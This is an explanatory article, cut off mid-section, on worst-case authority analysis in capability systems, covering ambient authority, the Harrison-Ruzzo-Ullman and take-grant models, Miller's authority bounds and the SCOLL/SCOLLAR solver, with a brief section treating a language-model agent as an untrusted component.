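# Worst-case authority analysis for language-model agents

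## What does it mean to bound a program without predicting it?

Worst-case authority analysis is a method in computer security for calculating a bound, or upper limit, on what a program could ever bring about, whatever its code contains. The analyst assumes that the program may do anything its access allows, rather than predicting what it will do, and uses what she knows about the components around it to work out which effects remain out of reach. The method comes from research on capability systems, a family of operating systems and programming languages that descends from a 1966 paper by Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn. Its best-developed form is SCOLL, a small language that Fred Spiessens and others at the Université catholique de Louvain designed for stating such problems to a solver.

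We need to bound programs without predicting them because people constantly run code they have not read. Miller and Shapiro's *Paradigm Regained* uses the card game Solitaire as an example. The game only needs to draw in its own window, receive clicks and keystrokes, and perhaps save to a file that the player picks. But on the Windows, Unix and Macintosh systems of the early 2000s, it ran with all the powers of the player who started it, so it could search her e-mail and sell what it found without breaking any of the operating system's rules. Power that a program has by default, without anyone granting it, is called ambient authority.

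The same paper compares two Unix commands that copy a file. The command `cp foo.txt bar.txt` gives the copying program two file names. The program has to open the files itself, so it must run with the power to open any file that the user could have named. In `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the user's shell opens the files and hands `cat` two open connections, one for reading and one for writing. In practice `cat` also runs with that ambient authority, but it does not need it for this job. If an operating system removed the authority and left only the two connections, the worst that `cat` could do, even if an attacker had rewritten it entirely, would be to put the wrong contents in `bar.txt`. We can establish this bound without predicting what `cat` will do. For `cp`, the same reasoning gives a bound that covers the user's whole file system.

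### How components come by references

In this literature, an object is a running piece of software that combines code with private state, which is a collection of references to other objects. Objects act on one another by sending messages along these references. Some languages let a program make up a reference, for instance by turning a number into a memory address. A capability is an unforgeable reference that both names a thing and permits its use. A program needs a capability to refer to the target at all, and once it has one it needs no further permission. Miller and Shapiro use the word only for references to things other than plain data, because access to data is a matter of knowledge. A program that can work out a number has that number, even if it is somebody's private key.

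In an object-capability system, components (objects, processes or larger modules) affect one another only by invoking references they hold. Java doesn't meet this condition, because one object can write to a static variable, which the whole program shares, and another can read it even though neither holds a reference to the other.

Where the condition does hold, a component can get a reference in only four ways. It may have the reference from the outset, as part of the initial conditions. It may create a new component, which gives it a reference to its child (parenthood). It may receive some of its parent's references when it is created (endowment). Finally, another component that already holds the reference may pass it on in a message (introduction). Spiessens (2007) stresses in *Patterns of Safe Collaboration* that a child gets nothing from its parent by default, so it starts with only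 what its parent chose to give it. The field gives components human names, so Alice, Bob and Carol in the small graph below are all programs. An arrow means "holds a reference to".

```
Before the message            After Alice sends Bob
                              a reference to Carol

Alice ----> Bob               Alice ----> Bob
  |                             |          |
  v                             v          |
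Carol                         Carol <------+
```

Alice could introduce Bob to Carol only because she already held references to both. If Bob holds a reference to Alice, he can also call her, and she can return a reference to Carol. In either case, the reference passes only if the code on one side sends it and the code on the other side accepts it (Jaradin, Spiessens and Van Roy, 2005, *SCOLL*). The slogan for this is "only connectivity begets connectivity". Two groups of components with no references between them can never acquire one, because any introduction requires a component that already holds references into both.

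Ambient authority invalidates this reasoning, and it can appear even in a design meant to prevent it. In Dennis and Van Horn's design, a process could run code it did not rely on inside a compartment with a chosen list of capabilities. But the code could still use an instruction that fetched shared capabilities by name, so it could escape confinement by fetching anything its launcher could fetch. Spiessens, who credits Charles Landau with noticing this, doubts that Dennis and Van Horn intended it. The later object-capability model omits the instruction.

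### Permission and authority

A permission is what a component may do directly to another component or resource. A component's authority is every effect it can cause, directly or through other components. Using a permission is the simplest form of authority, and most of the difficulty in analyzing authority comes from indirect effects.

Spiessens uses the example of a screen to distinguish permission from authority. Alice has permission to manipulate the screen and to read from Bob, but Bob has no permission to touch the screen. Alice's code reads instructions from Bob and carries them out, so whatever Bob asks for appears on the screen as if he had permission to put it there. A table of permissions would make Bob look harmless. If somebody rewrote Alice's code to ignore Bob's instructions, he would lose his authority over the screen, but the table would stay the same.

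Because authority depends on behaviour, a program's code can also reduce it. Suppose Alice's job requires only one region of the screen. Giving her permission to manipulate the screen may satisfy a rule of granting only the permissions she needs, but it gives her access to every pixel. A proxy, a component that passes on only part of a resource's power, can restrict her further. Alice receives a reference to a screen proxy, and only the proxy holds a reference to the screen driver. The proxy's code crops every drawing instruction to the agreed region before relaying it. This limits Alice's authority, and the authority Bob exercises through her, to that region.

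Cropping deals with only one harm. Alice could still draw a convincing copy of the system's password dialog inside her region. To address this, Spiessens describes a different restriction, in which the software engineer gives untrusted code only a few purpose-built drawing routines that put a recognizable border and colour scheme around everything they render.

Permission and authority are easy to confuse. Nicol (2026), in *Permity*, proposed merging the two words into one, in a thread on cap-talk, a mailing list for people who work on capabilities. Alan Karp replied with the example of a web server. Only the administrator and the server have permission to read the file that contains the home page, so an analysis of permissions alone would conclude that secrets in the file are safe. Yet any stranger who requests the page makes the server read the file and return its contents, so the stranger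 has the authority to read the file without having the permission. Miller, in the same thread, thought the words were fine but poorly taught, and conceded that "even among ourselves we misstate it"; his example was the claim that authority is about reachability. That claim fails because a server that refused every request would leave the same path in the graph from stranger to file, but would give the stranger nothing.

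### Assuming the worst

In general, nobody can predict whether Bob will one day obtain a reference to Carol, because that depends on the code and state of everything that might pass him one. Miller and Shapiro argue that an analyst can instead compute a conservative bound, which gives either a reliable "no" or a "maybe". If she uses only the present arrangement of references, she treats every program as hostile. If she also considers how some of the programs behave, she can rule out more effects and turn some of the "maybes" into "no". They complain that three decades of formal work used only the arrangement, which leaves out components like the cropping proxy, and so produced false proofs that capability systems could not enforce ordinary policies. Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues (2016), in *Permission and Authority Revisited*, later defined the informal notions in a small formal language,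 with separate bounds for current and eventual authority, and for topology and behaviour.

*SCOLL and SCOLLAR* (Spiessens, Jaradin and Van Roy, 2005) gives the example of a program that will load two outside components, X and Y. X needs the screen and Y needs the internet. Either component could mount a phishing attack if it had both, making the user believe she is on her bank's site while she is connected to the attacker's. Withholding the internet from X and the screen from Y is not enough, because the two can cooperate, with X drawing the bank's pages and Y sending what the user types to the attacker. Another part of the program, the main program, has to deal with both X and Y and holds a reference to each.

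Suppose first that the analyst knows nothing about the main program. The program may then send X a reference to Y, X may pass Y anything, and Y may send that out over the internet. The answer is therefore "maybe", and the fake bank stays on the list of possible effects.

Suppose she has read the main program and found that it never gives X a reference to Y, or Y a reference to X, and never passes anything between them. X begins with its reference to the screen, and perhaps one to the main program. Any children it creates can receive only what X holds. Only the main program could introduce X to Y, and it does not. As long as the system enforces the four rules, X will therefore never reach Y or the internet, and the answer is "no". This answer holds for every program that X might be, including one written by an attacker who had read this analysis.

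The clause about carrying things matters as much as the one about references, because if the main program copies text from X into its messages to Y, X influences what leaves the machine without holding a reference to Y. According to the same report, two untrusted components can exchange data through a third whenever one can affect its behaviour and the other can observe the effect. The components also have to be separated in advance. Spiessens notes that once one of two untrusted components holds a capability to the other, nothing can restrict what flows between them, so designers always aim to keep at least one dependable component in between.

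X and Y are untrusted components, so the analysis assumes they may do anything their references allow. X may be well written, but the analysis doesn't depend on that. The main program in the second case is a relied-upon component, which means the analyst knows its code well enough to count on what it will not do. The analyst can sometimes establish this from very little code. For example, Spiessens gives a procedure a few lines long that accepts an input and passes it to Bob. From those lines alone, a programmer can tell that the procedure returns nothing to its callers, uses no reference except the one to Bob, and ignores whatever Bob sends back.

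An analysis is sound if it never understates what can happen, though it may overstate it. When a sound analysis concludes that an effect is impossible, one can rely on that conclusion. Soundness requires the model to cover every component, including those created only in unusual runs of the software. Soundness alone is easy to achieve, because one can model any software as a single component with unrestricted behaviour, as Spiessens observes. That model is sound, but every effect is reachable in it, so it rules out nothing. A useful bound must also be tight, meaning that it allows for little more than what can really happen.

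A "maybe" means that some program fitting the analyst's description could cause the harm, but the real program may be more restricted than the description. The analyst can try to resolve this by describing the relied-upon parts more precisely. For example, the first description might say that a component may return a certain reference when called, and a closer look at the code might show that it returns the reference only to a caller who supplied a particular token in the same call. The analyst cannot do this for the untrusted parts, because the analysis assumes no knowledge of them. For those parts, the bound can shrink only if they hold fewer references, or if a relied-upon component controls what those references allow.

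### The language model in the place of X

A language model is a program, trained on very large amounts of text, that produces text in response to text. It does not act on the world by itself. An agent combines a language model with a harness, which is software that holds passwords and other credentials and carries out the model's tool calls. A tool call is a structured request for an action, such as sending a given message to a given address. Both the user's instructions and the contents of strangers' web pages and e-mails reach the model as text. In prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by placing text in what the model reads so that the model follows it as an instruction.

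A language-model agent seems to fit the older scheme in some respects. The harness is code that people can inspect, and the model would take the place of X, since nobody can work out its behavior from its internals as they could with a short procedure. The difference is that X and Y could be kept apart because each needed only one resource. An agent that answers its user's mail needs both her private correspondence and a way to send messages, and the worst it could do with the two together is bad. Removing either would make the bound reassuring but the agent useless. The question is whether a bound that treats the model as untrusted can exclude enough harm while leaving the agent able to work.

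## Can the exact bound be computed?

No algorithm can compute the exact bound for every system, even if the analyst assumes the worst about every program in it. With that assumption, the analyst doesn't need to predict what each program will do, but the bound still depends on the rules by which programs may pass permissions to one another. In the 1970s, researchers showed that some sets of rules make the bound impossible to compute in general, while others allow an exact answer in time proportional to the size of the system.

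### The access matrix

*Protection in Operating Systems* (Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman, 1976) describes a system's permissions as a table called an access matrix. Each row stands for a subject, such as a running program, and each column for an object, which in this older literature means anything a right can apply to, including a file or another subject. Each cell lists the rights the row's subject has over the column's object.

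Commands change the matrix. A command may begin with conditions, each testing whether a certain right is in a certain cell. If all the conditions hold, the command carries out a fixed sequence of operations, with no loops or branches. The six possible operations are entering or deleting a right, creating or destroying a subject, and creating or destroying an object.

In one of the paper's examples, any process may create a file, which makes it the owner, and an owner may confer the right to read, write or execute the file on anyone. Sam creates two files, lets Joe execute one and lets him read the other:

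| | Sam | Joe | Code | Data |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| **Sam** | | | own | own |
| **Joe** | | | execute | read |

The safety question is whether any sequence of commands, starting from a given matrix, can enter a given right into a cell that lacked it. This is a worst-case question because the commands may come in any order. The answer can be trivial, as with the right to read Data, which can spread because Sam owns Data and can let anyone read it. To avoid such answers, Harrison and colleagues advise deleting trusted subjects from the matrix before asking the question. Once Sam's row is deleted, nobody owns Data, so Joe cannot pass on his right to read it.

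### Why no algorithm answers the question in general

The proof uses Turing machines, which are idealised computers with an endless tape of cells, a head that reads and writes one symbol at a time, and a finite table of instructions. No algorithm can tell, for every such machine, whether it will ever reach its final state. Harrison and colleagues show that an access matrix can simulate any Turing machine.

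Each tape cell becomes a subject. The symbol in the cell becomes a right that this subject holds over itself. The subject under the head also holds a right that stands for the machine's current state. Each subject owns its right-hand neighbour, which keeps the cells in order, and the last subject holds a marker called "end". If the tape reads W, X, Y, Z and the machine is in state q with its head on the second cell, the matrix looks like this:

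| | s1 | s2 | s3 | s4 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| **s1** | W | own | | |
| **s2** | | X, q | own | |
| **s3** | | | Y | own |
| **s4** | | | | Z, end |

Suppose that in state q, on reading X, the machine writes V, moves left and enters state p. The matching command checks that s1 owns s2 and that s2 holds q and X over itself. It then deletes q and X, enters V in the same cell, and gives s1 the right p over itself. When the head moves past the end of the tape, another command creates a new subject and transfers the end marker to it. At most one command applies at a time, so the matrix has to follow the machine step by step. The right that stands for the final state appears in the matrix only if the machine reaches that state. An algorithm that could always answer the safety question could therefore also decide whether any given Turing machine reaches its final state, which is impossible.

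The argument works even for one fixed set of commands. Some Turing machines can simulate any other, and if the commands simulate one of these, no algorithm can decide for every starting matrix whether it is safe.

Some systems can still be analyzed. Harrison and colleagues compare the problem to ambiguity in the grammars of programming languages. No algorithm can tell whether an arbitrary grammar is ambiguous, but language designers can use a class of grammars for which a test exists. In *Robust Composition*, Miller (2006) writes that the 1976 result shows it is possible, and "depressingly easy", to design rules under which nobody can calculate how permissions will spread. He complains that readers often take it to mean that this can never be calculated under any rules. He counts at least three protection systems for which researchers have shown that safety is decidable.

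### Which restrictions help

Imitating a Turing machine requires creating new subjects to serve as additional tape. If no command can create anything, the matrix has only finitely many possible states, and an algorithm can in principle search them all. This case includes every real computer, because memory is always limited, but the search can still take too long to be practical. Harrison and colleagues prove that the problem without creation is among the hardest solvable with a reasonable amount of memory, which probably means that the time needed grows exponentially with the size of the problem.

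Forbidding deletion alone doesn't make safety decidable. *The Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Model*, a set of Purdue University lecture slides, lists safety as undecidable even for monotonic systems, where rights can't be removed once entered.

Harrison and colleagues found an algorithm for systems in which every command performs a single operation. Such a command cannot both create a subject and give it a right, so all new subjects start out identical and the analyst needs to consider only one. Harrison and colleagues admit that these systems are "not terribly realistic". Even creating a file takes two operations in their examples, one to make the file and one to record its owner.

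Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman's proof also contained a mistake. It ignores commands that delete rights, on the grounds that deletion can never help a right to leak. Tripunitara and Li, in *The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*, point out that deletion can help, because the original paper's formal definition counts a leak whenever a right enters a cell that lacked it immediately before. If every cell already holds the right and no command can create new cells, a leak requires deleting the right from a cell and entering it again. Tripunitara and Li repair the proof, and its conclusion still holds. They also prove that safety remains undecidable in general under the more natural definition, which compares each cell with its contents at the start.

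Even under such restrictions, safety can be hard to decide. Next Generation Access Control (NGAC) is an American standard that represents permissions as a graph. Edges link users to attributes such as "student", and attributes to resources. A user can reach a resource if a path of suitable edges leads to it. *Safety Analysis in the NGAC Model* (Tan, Davies and colleagues, 2025) shows that safety is decidable but coNP-complete when the possible users, attributes and resources are finite and each command performs one operation. A short list of commands can prove that a system is unsafe, but it is not expected that every safe system has a comparably short proof of its safety.

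The exact bound is hard to compute because some commands test whether something is absent. An organisation may require that nobody be both a teacher and a student, so the command that makes someone a teacher first checks that the person isn't a student. Some permissions therefore exclude others, and the analyst cannot simply add up everything the commands could permit. Tan and colleagues propose an algorithm that lists every largest set of edges that can exist together and looks for a forbidden path in each. This is much faster than trying every combination, but the number of sets can still grow exponentially. If each of ten users must be a teacher, a student or a member of staff, there are 3^10, or 59,049, sets to examine, and each further user triples the number. Tan and colleagues point out that groups of three mutually exclusive attributes are the worst possible input for their algorithm,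 and also a common one. They have not yet tested the algorithm on real data.

### The take-grant model

The take-grant model goes the other way and fixes the rules once and for all. Jones, Lipton and Snyder introduced it in 1976, and Bishop and Snyder (1979), in *The Transfer of Information and Authority in a Protection System*, extended it. A system is a graph whose nodes are subjects, which can act, and objects, which cannot. An arrow from one node to another carries one or more rights: read, write, take and grant. Four rules change the graph, and only a subject can apply them:

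- **Take.** If Alice has the take right over Bob, she can acquire any right that Bob holds.
- **Grant.** If Alice has the grant right over Bob, she can give him any right that she holds.
- **Create.** Alice can create a new node and have any rights over it.
- **Remove.** Alice can give up any of her own rights.

The remove rule never helps a right to spread, since an extra arrow does no harm to whoever wants it. The create rule matters a great deal, as a graph of five nodes shows. Carol, Alice and Bob are subjects, while Folder and File are objects:

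```
Carol --read--> Alice --grant--> Bob --take--> Folder --read--> File
```

Can Alice acquire the right to read File? Her only right is to give things to Bob, so one might think not. But the following sequence works:

1. Bob takes the right to read File from Folder.
2. Alice creates an object called Box, with take and grant rights over it.
3. Alice grants Bob the grant right over Box.
4. Bob grants Box the right to read File.
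5. Alice takes that right from Box.

The direction of the arrow between Alice and Bob does not matter, because Alice can always make a box and tell Bob where it is. Bishop and Snyder call a group of subjects an island if arrows with take or grant rights, pointing in either direction, connect them all without passing through an object. Any right that one subject on an island holds can reach every other subject on it. Alice and Bob form an island, and Carol, who has only a read arrow, is an island by herself.

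Rights can also cross between islands through objects, if the objects lie on what Bishop and Snyder call a bridge. Suppose a passive object, Tray, separates Alice from Bob. If Alice may take from Tray and Bob may grant to it, he can leave a right there for her to collect. If Alice may grant and Bob may take, she can leave him a grant right over a new box, and the sequence above completes the transfer. The transfer fails if both may only take, because neither can put a right in Tray, or if both may only grant, because neither can get one out. In general, a bridge is a path between two subjects that has one of two forms. Either it consists of take arrows that all point the same way, or it has a single grant arrow, in either direction, and any take arrows on either side point inwards from the two ends.

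A subject can acquire a right over some node exactly when three conditions hold. Some node must already hold the right. A subject must be that node or be able to reach it along a chain of take arrows, as Bob reaches Folder. A series of islands, each joined to the next by a bridge, must lead from that subject to the one acquiring the right. If an object is to acquire the right, some subject must also be able to grant to it, perhaps after a chain of takes. An algorithm can check these conditions in time proportional to the size of the graph.

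The answer is exact, even though subjects may create new nodes without limit. Bishop and Snyder's proof for their extended model shows that every newly created part of the graph connects to the old part through a single subject, which can act on its behalf, so the analyst never needs to follow the new nodes individually. In the 1976 model, by contrast, commands can link any number of new subjects into a Turing machine tape.

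### Information without permission

By this test, Carol can never acquire the right to read File, since no take or grant arrow touches her. She may still learn what File contains, because Alice can acquire the right to read it, and Carol can read Alice. Bishop and Snyder call a transfer of rights de jure and a transfer of information without the right de facto. In their simplest example, Charlie copies a private file into a shared mailbox, and Baker reads the copy. Baker never holds a right to the file, and he depends on Charlie to copy it accurately and keep the copy up to date.

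They add four de facto rules to the model. Each puts a dashed "read" arrow in the graph, which marks a possible flow of information:

- **Post.** One subject writes to a node and another subject reads from it.
- **Pass.** A subject reads one node and writes what it finds to another.
- **Spy.** A subject reads from a second subject, which reads from a third node.
- **Find.** One subject writes to a second, which writes to a further node.

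The rules can be applied again to the dashed arrows, so information may travel a long way. It stops where two objects are adjacent, with no subject between them to pass it on.

Carol needs both sets of rules. The take and grant rules give Alice the right to read File, and the spy rule then gives Carol its contents. The de facto rules alone cannot cross the grant arrow between Alice and Bob, and the de jure rules alone cannot cross the read arrow between Carol and Alice. Bishop and Snyder prove that the combined rules also have an exact test that takes time proportional to the size of the graph.

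All these results assume what Bishop and Snyder call perfect cooperation, which they concede may be prudent but unrealistic. They mention two ways to relax it. One is to ask whether a right could spread without its owners' help. The other is to count the conspirators a transfer requires and treat transfers that require more of them as less likely. For Carol to learn the contents of File, she, Alice and Bob must all cooperate. That count is informative if three independent people control the three programs, but it means little if one attacker wrote them all.

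### Miller's bounds

Perfect cooperation is one end of a range, and what the actual programs will do is the other. Miller, who credits Bishop and Snyder with inspiring his idea of authority, arranges the possibilities into seven quantities. Each is a set of facts of the form "Bob can access Carol", and the last column gives his description of how hard the set is to calculate.

| Set | Contents | Calculation |
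|---|---|---|
| CP | Current permissions | trivial |
| EP | Permissions that components will eventually have | intractable |
| BP | Bound on EP that takes account of some components' behaviour | interesting |
| TP | Bound on EP from the arrangement of permissions alone | easy |
| EA | Authority that components will eventually have | intractable |
| BA | Bound on EA that takes account of some components' behaviour | interesting |
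| TA | Bound on EA from the arrangement of permissions alone | easy |

The sets contain one another as follows, where "A ⊆ B" means that everything in A is also in B:

```
CP ⊆ EP ⊆ BP ⊆ TP
EA ⊆ BA ⊆ TA
EP ⊆ EA      BP ⊆ BA      TP ⊆ TA
```

Along each line, every set contains the one before it, because the analyst uses less information. A fact missing from TA or BA is therefore also missing from EA, so the analyst can rely on its absence. Each permission set also lies inside the corresponding authority set, because using a permission directly is one way to have an effect. But a fact's absence from a permission set doesn't rule out the effect. For example, TP doesn't include Carol's access to File, but she can still learn what File contains.

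EA is the exact answer, but it is infeasible to compute. TA is easy to compute, and anything missing from it is also missing from EA, but it includes authority that EA does not. Miller recommends BA, which he describes as the smallest of these sets that is both safe and tractable.

In the five-node graph, TA includes Carol's access to the contents of File. Suppose the analyst reads Bob's code and finds that he uses File only for his own calculations, never grants a right, never writes anything, and reveals nothing to those who can observe him. Step 4 of the sequence then never happens, and Bob provides no other route. Alice and Carol may still do whatever their rights allow, but neither can learn what File contains. BA therefore excludes Carol's access, although the arrows in the graph are the same.

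Miller defined these quantities in ordinary language. Drossopoulou and colleagues later formalised them and set out how the definitions relate to one another, so one can try to prove that one bound contains another.

### What the arrangement alone can rule out

The bound that uses only the arrangement is weakest in object-capability systems, where it would be most useful. Nearly every node in such a system is a component with code, and components pass references whenever one calls another. Suppose Alice holds a reference to Bob and both may do anything. Alice can call Bob and send him every reference she holds, including one to herself, and Bob can answer with every reference he holds. After one exchange, each has every reference the other had, and it no longer matters which of them held the original reference to the other.

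The same happens along every other arrow. If five components are in a row, each with a reference to the next, there are four references at the start. The middle three introduce their neighbours to one another, those neighbours do the same, and eventually every component holds a reference to each of the other four, for a total of twenty references. Adding components or rearranging the arrows changes the number, but every connected part of the graph still ends up sharing everything. The bound can therefore exclude an effect only if no path joins the component to the resource, even when the direction of the arrows is ignored.

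Few useful programs have parts that are so completely separate. A main program that loads a screen component and an internet component must hold references to both, so under the bound the screen component could gain internet access. For the same reason, the topology-only bound cannot show that revocation works. Suppose Alice wants to give Bob temporary access to Carol. She can give him a reference to a small forwarding component that relays his messages to Carol until Alice switches it off. Because Bob, the forwarder and Carol are connected, the bound includes the possibility that the forwarder gives Bob its own reference to Carol, which Alice could never take back. The forwarder's code, only a few lines long, shows that it does not do this. Miller lists this kind of revocation and confinement (isolating an untrusted program so that it cannot leak what it learns) among the policies that false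 proofs about capability systems ruled out.

To get a more informative bound, the analyst has to describe how some components behave, in a form simple enough that the calculation still ends. Spiessens's knowledge behaviour models do this by extending the take-grant model with rules for what each component may be willing to do.

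## How do SCOLL and SCOLLAR calculate a bound?

SCOLL is a notation for describing a group of components, the references they hold and the conditions under which each will cooperate with the others. The SCOLLAR solver reads this description and works out what the components could cause. Both are based on Spiessens's knowledge behaviour models.

### What a model contains

A knowledge behaviour model has a finite set of subjects, which stand for the components of the software. The rest of the model consists of facts about those subjects and rules for deriving new facts from old ones.

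Permission facts record who holds a reference to whom. Behaviour facts record what a subject may be willing to do. Knowledge facts record which interactions have succeeded, from the point of view of one participant. For software whose components call one another, a few kinds of fact are enough:

| Fact | Kind | Meaning |
|---|---|---|
| access(A, B) | permission | A holds a reference to B |
| may.sendTo(A, B, X) | behaviour | A may call B and pass it a reference to X |
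| may.receive(B) | behaviour | B may accept references that callers pass to it |
| may.getFrom(A, B) | behaviour | A may call B and accept what B returns |
| may.return(B, Y) | behaviour | B may return a reference to Y when called |
| did.receive(B, X) | knowledge | some caller has passed X to B |
| did.getFrom(A, B, Y) | knowledge | A has called B and got Y back |

The fact may.return(carol, carol) means that the analyst, given what she knows about Carol's code, can't rule out that Carol returns a reference to herself. These predicate names come from Spiessens's thesis. The 2005 report by Spiessens and colleagues uses shorter ones, such as iEmit for may.sendTo and rEmit for may.return.

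System rules describe what the programming language or operating system permits, so they apply to every subject. In an object-capability system, two of them govern the passing of references. Everything to the left of the arrow must hold before the facts on the right follow:

```
access(A,B)  access(A,X)  may.sendTo(A,B,X)  may.receive(B)
    =>  access(B,X)  did.sendTo(A,B,X)  did.receive(B,X)

access(A,B)  access(B,Y)  may.getFrom(A,B)  may.return(B,Y)
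    =>  access(A,Y)  did.getFrom(A,B,Y)  did.return(B,Y)
```

The upper rule covers introduction by the caller, and the lower rule covers references the caller receives as return values. Further rules cover parenthood and endowment, which need no cooperation from the child.

Behaviour rules describe the code of one particular subject. They have knowledge on the left and behaviour on the right, so they express how the subject reacts to what has happened to it. For example, a forwarder that hands its callers whatever its target returned has the rule:

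```
did.getFrom(forwarder, target, Y)  =>  may.return(forwarder, Y)
```

An untrusted subject gets the behaviour that the 2005 report calls MAXIMAL, a single rule with no conditions that allows every kind of behaviour. If Bob has MAXIMAL behaviour, he calls every subject he can reach, offers it everything he holds, and accepts and returns whatever he can. Only the system rules and the unwillingness of other subjects limit him. No program an attacker puts in Bob's place can do more than this, at least among the behaviours the model can express.

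### Why the calculation ends

No rule contains the word "not". New knowledge can only make a subject willing to do more, and a new reference can only make more interactions possible. Facts therefore accumulate and never disappear. Let X be the set of facts so far, Sys(X) the facts that the system rules derive from it, and Beh(X) the facts that the behaviour rules derive. One round of the calculation then gives:

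```
E(X) = X ∪ Sys(X) ∪ Beh(X)
```

The analyst starts from the initial facts and applies the rules repeatedly until a round adds no new facts. The resulting set of facts, called the fixpoint, is the bound. In Miller's terms, it is the kind of bound that takes some components' behaviour into account.

Spiessens and colleagues prove that the fixpoint is computable whenever the set of subjects is finite, because there are then only finitely many possible facts. Five subjects, for example, allow 25 access facts and 125 facts of the form may.sendTo(A, B, X). The calculation stops when a round adds no new facts. The order of the rules doesn't matter, because applying one rule never invalidates the conditions for another. Spiessens gives the running time as polynomial in the size of the model.

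A program can keep creating new components for as long as it runs, so a finite model can cover them all only through aggregation, which means modelling many components as one subject. By default, the subject Bob stands for the program called Bob and everything it creates, directly or indirectly. The combined subject holds every reference that any member holds, and its behaviour includes everything any member would do. Other subjects treat it as they would treat any of its members.

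Aggregation can make the analysis report access that could never happen, but it can't hide access that could. If the combined model never gives Bob's group access to Carol's group, then no member of Bob's group can ever reach a member of Carol's. Jaradin and colleagues wrote out the proof for a predecessor of knowledge behaviour models. The combined model allows any single step that the original system allows, such as Alice sending Bob a reference to Carol, because the combined counterparts of Alice and Bob hold at least the same references and are at least as willing to take part. Repeating the argument for each step shows that the combined model can follow any history of the original, however long. Spiessens and colleagues state the corresponding theorem for knowledge behaviour models.

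Aggregating untrusted components does little to loosen the bound, because a subject that may already do anything doesn't become less restricted when it gains members. But aggregating relied-upon components can make the bound much looser. Suppose Alice sets up two forwarders, one that lets Bob use Carol and one that lets Dave use Erin. If the analyst models both forwarders as one subject, that subject holds references to Carol and Erin and serves both Bob and Dave, so Bob appears able to use Erin. This false alarm disappears if the analyst splits the subject in two and recalculates. Spiessens and colleagues show that each split in a series gives a sound bound that is no looser than the one before.

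### The caretaker

Alice can give Bob temporary access to Carol through a forwarder called a caretaker, after a design that Redell published in 1974. The caretaker's code never gives out its own reference to Carol. The open question is how Carol must behave for Alice to be able to revoke Bob's access.

Spiessens and colleagues model this with five subjects. They rely on Alice and the caretaker, whose behaviour rules follow from their intended code. Bob is untrusted and gets MAXIMAL behaviour. So does Dave, a component to which only Carol holds a reference at first. Once Alice has set things up, the references look like this (Alice also holds one to Bob):

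```
Bob ----> Caretaker ----> Carol ----> Dave
              ^             ^
              |             |
              +--- Alice ---+
```

Suppose that Carol may return a reference to herself when somebody calls her. Many ordinary objects do this, so that programmers can write several calls to the same object in a row. The rules then lead to the following facts:

| Step | Rule | What it adds |
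|---|---|---|
| 1 | Alice's behaviour | Alice may create the caretaker, endow it with Carol and send it to Bob |
| 2 | System: parenthood | access(alice, caretaker) |
| 3 | System: endowment | access(caretaker, carol), and the caretaker learns that Carol is its target |
| 4 | System: sending | access(bob, caretaker), since Bob accepts everything |
| 5 | Caretaker's behaviour | may.getFrom(caretaker, carol) |
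| 6 | System: returning | did.getFrom(caretaker, carol, carol) |
| 7 | Caretaker's behaviour | may.return(caretaker, carol) |
| 8 | System: returning | access(bob, carol) |

Bob now holds Carol directly. Alice can switch the caretaker off, but he will go on calling Carol without it.

The caretaker has held a reference to Carol since step 3, so step 6 adds only the knowledge that Carol came back as a return value. The caretaker's code passes return values on to the caller, so in step 7 it becomes willing to hand over a reference that it would otherwise have kept. An analysis that tracked only references would have included access(bob, carol) from the start, because everybody here is connected, whereas the behaviour rules make that result depend on what Carol does.

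### Safety goals and liveness goals

The analyst has to give SCOLLAR safety and liveness goals. A safety goal is a fact that must stay out of the fixpoint, and SCOLL marks it with an exclamation mark, as in `!access(bob, carol)` in this example. A liveness goal is a fact that the fixpoint must contain. Spiessens and colleagues use `access(bob, dave)` to represent Carol being able to do her job, which here means giving Bob a reference to Dave.

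Without a liveness goal, the problem has a useless answer, because a system in which nothing works is safe. For example, Carol is safe if she never responds to anybody.

Safety goals deserve more confidence than liveness goals, because a fact missing from the fixpoint reliably can't come true, while a fact in the fixpoint only might. Spiessens says explicitly that liveness goals prove nothing about what the software will or can achieve. They only rule out solutions whose restrictions would certainly prevent the wanted effect.

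### How SCOLLAR searches

Calculating one fixpoint shows whether Carol is safe with one particular behaviour. SCOLLAR can also search for every way of restricting Carol that meets the goals and forbids no more than necessary. In the SCOLL program, the analyst marks Carol as a subject to search for and gives her a minimal starting behaviour, which here is empty.

The solver uses constraint programming. Each rule of the model becomes a process that adds information to a common store and never removes any. In the first implementation, described by Jaradin and colleagues, the processes run until they have nothing new to add. If some of Carol's possible actions are still undecided, the solver picks one and assumes that she may do it. It goes back and forbids the action only if this assumption fails. The first solution is therefore one to which no further action can safely be added. Extra constraints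 then stop the solver from reporting stricter versions of solutions it has already found.

The absence of "not" also speeds up the search. Once Bob has reached Carol in a partial solution, allowing Carol to do more cannot undo that, so the solver can discard every extension of that solution without checking it. The caretaker problem had 2^40 possibilities, or about 1.1 trillion. SCOLLAR examined 670 of them and found five alternative sets of restrictions on Carol in less than five seconds.

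All five forbid Carol to return herself when called, which blocks step 6 of the leak. They also forbid her to send herself to Dave. The liveness goal requires that Bob can reach Dave, and because both are untrusted, Bob can get whatever Dave holds.

The shortest solutions have four prohibitions. In one of them, Carol may not return herself, send herself to Dave, accept anything that Dave returns, or accept any reference from a caller. She never learns of anyone except Dave, so she can't leak herself to anyone else. She is also of limited use, because many services need callers to pass them something to work on. Another solution has eight prohibitions but lets Carol accept references from callers. She may not send herself to Alice, Bob or Dave, or return herself in exchange for a reference to Alice, Bob, Dave or the caretaker. She may still return herself to a caller who has just sent her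 a reference to Carol, since that caller already has that reference.

Several solutions exist because some actions are harmless separately and harmful together. Jaradin and colleagues give an example from their slightly different model of the caretaker. Carol may send herself to Alice, or she may let Bob have a reference to Alice, but not both. Alice doesn't check where her references come from, and she will pass Carol on to Bob if she received Carol as an argument in a call. The programmer who writes Carol can choose which of the two actions Carol needs.

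One of the five solutions does not seem to fit the program that the report prints. It forbids Carol to return herself, to send herself to Bob or Dave, and to accept references from callers, but lets her accept what Dave returns and send herself to Alice. Under the printed rules, the following can happen:

1. Alice calls Carol and gets a reference to Dave.
2. Alice sends Dave a reference to herself, as her rules allow for anything she has obtained in this way.
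3. Carol calls Dave, who returns the reference to Alice.
4. Carol sends herself to Alice.
5. Alice sends Carol to Dave, who shares everything with Bob.

The printed program also lacks a closing bracket, so a misprint is more likely than a fault in the solver. The two solutions described in detail above do not allow this leak. Still, even a pattern with five subjects is hard to check by eye.

### Refining a model

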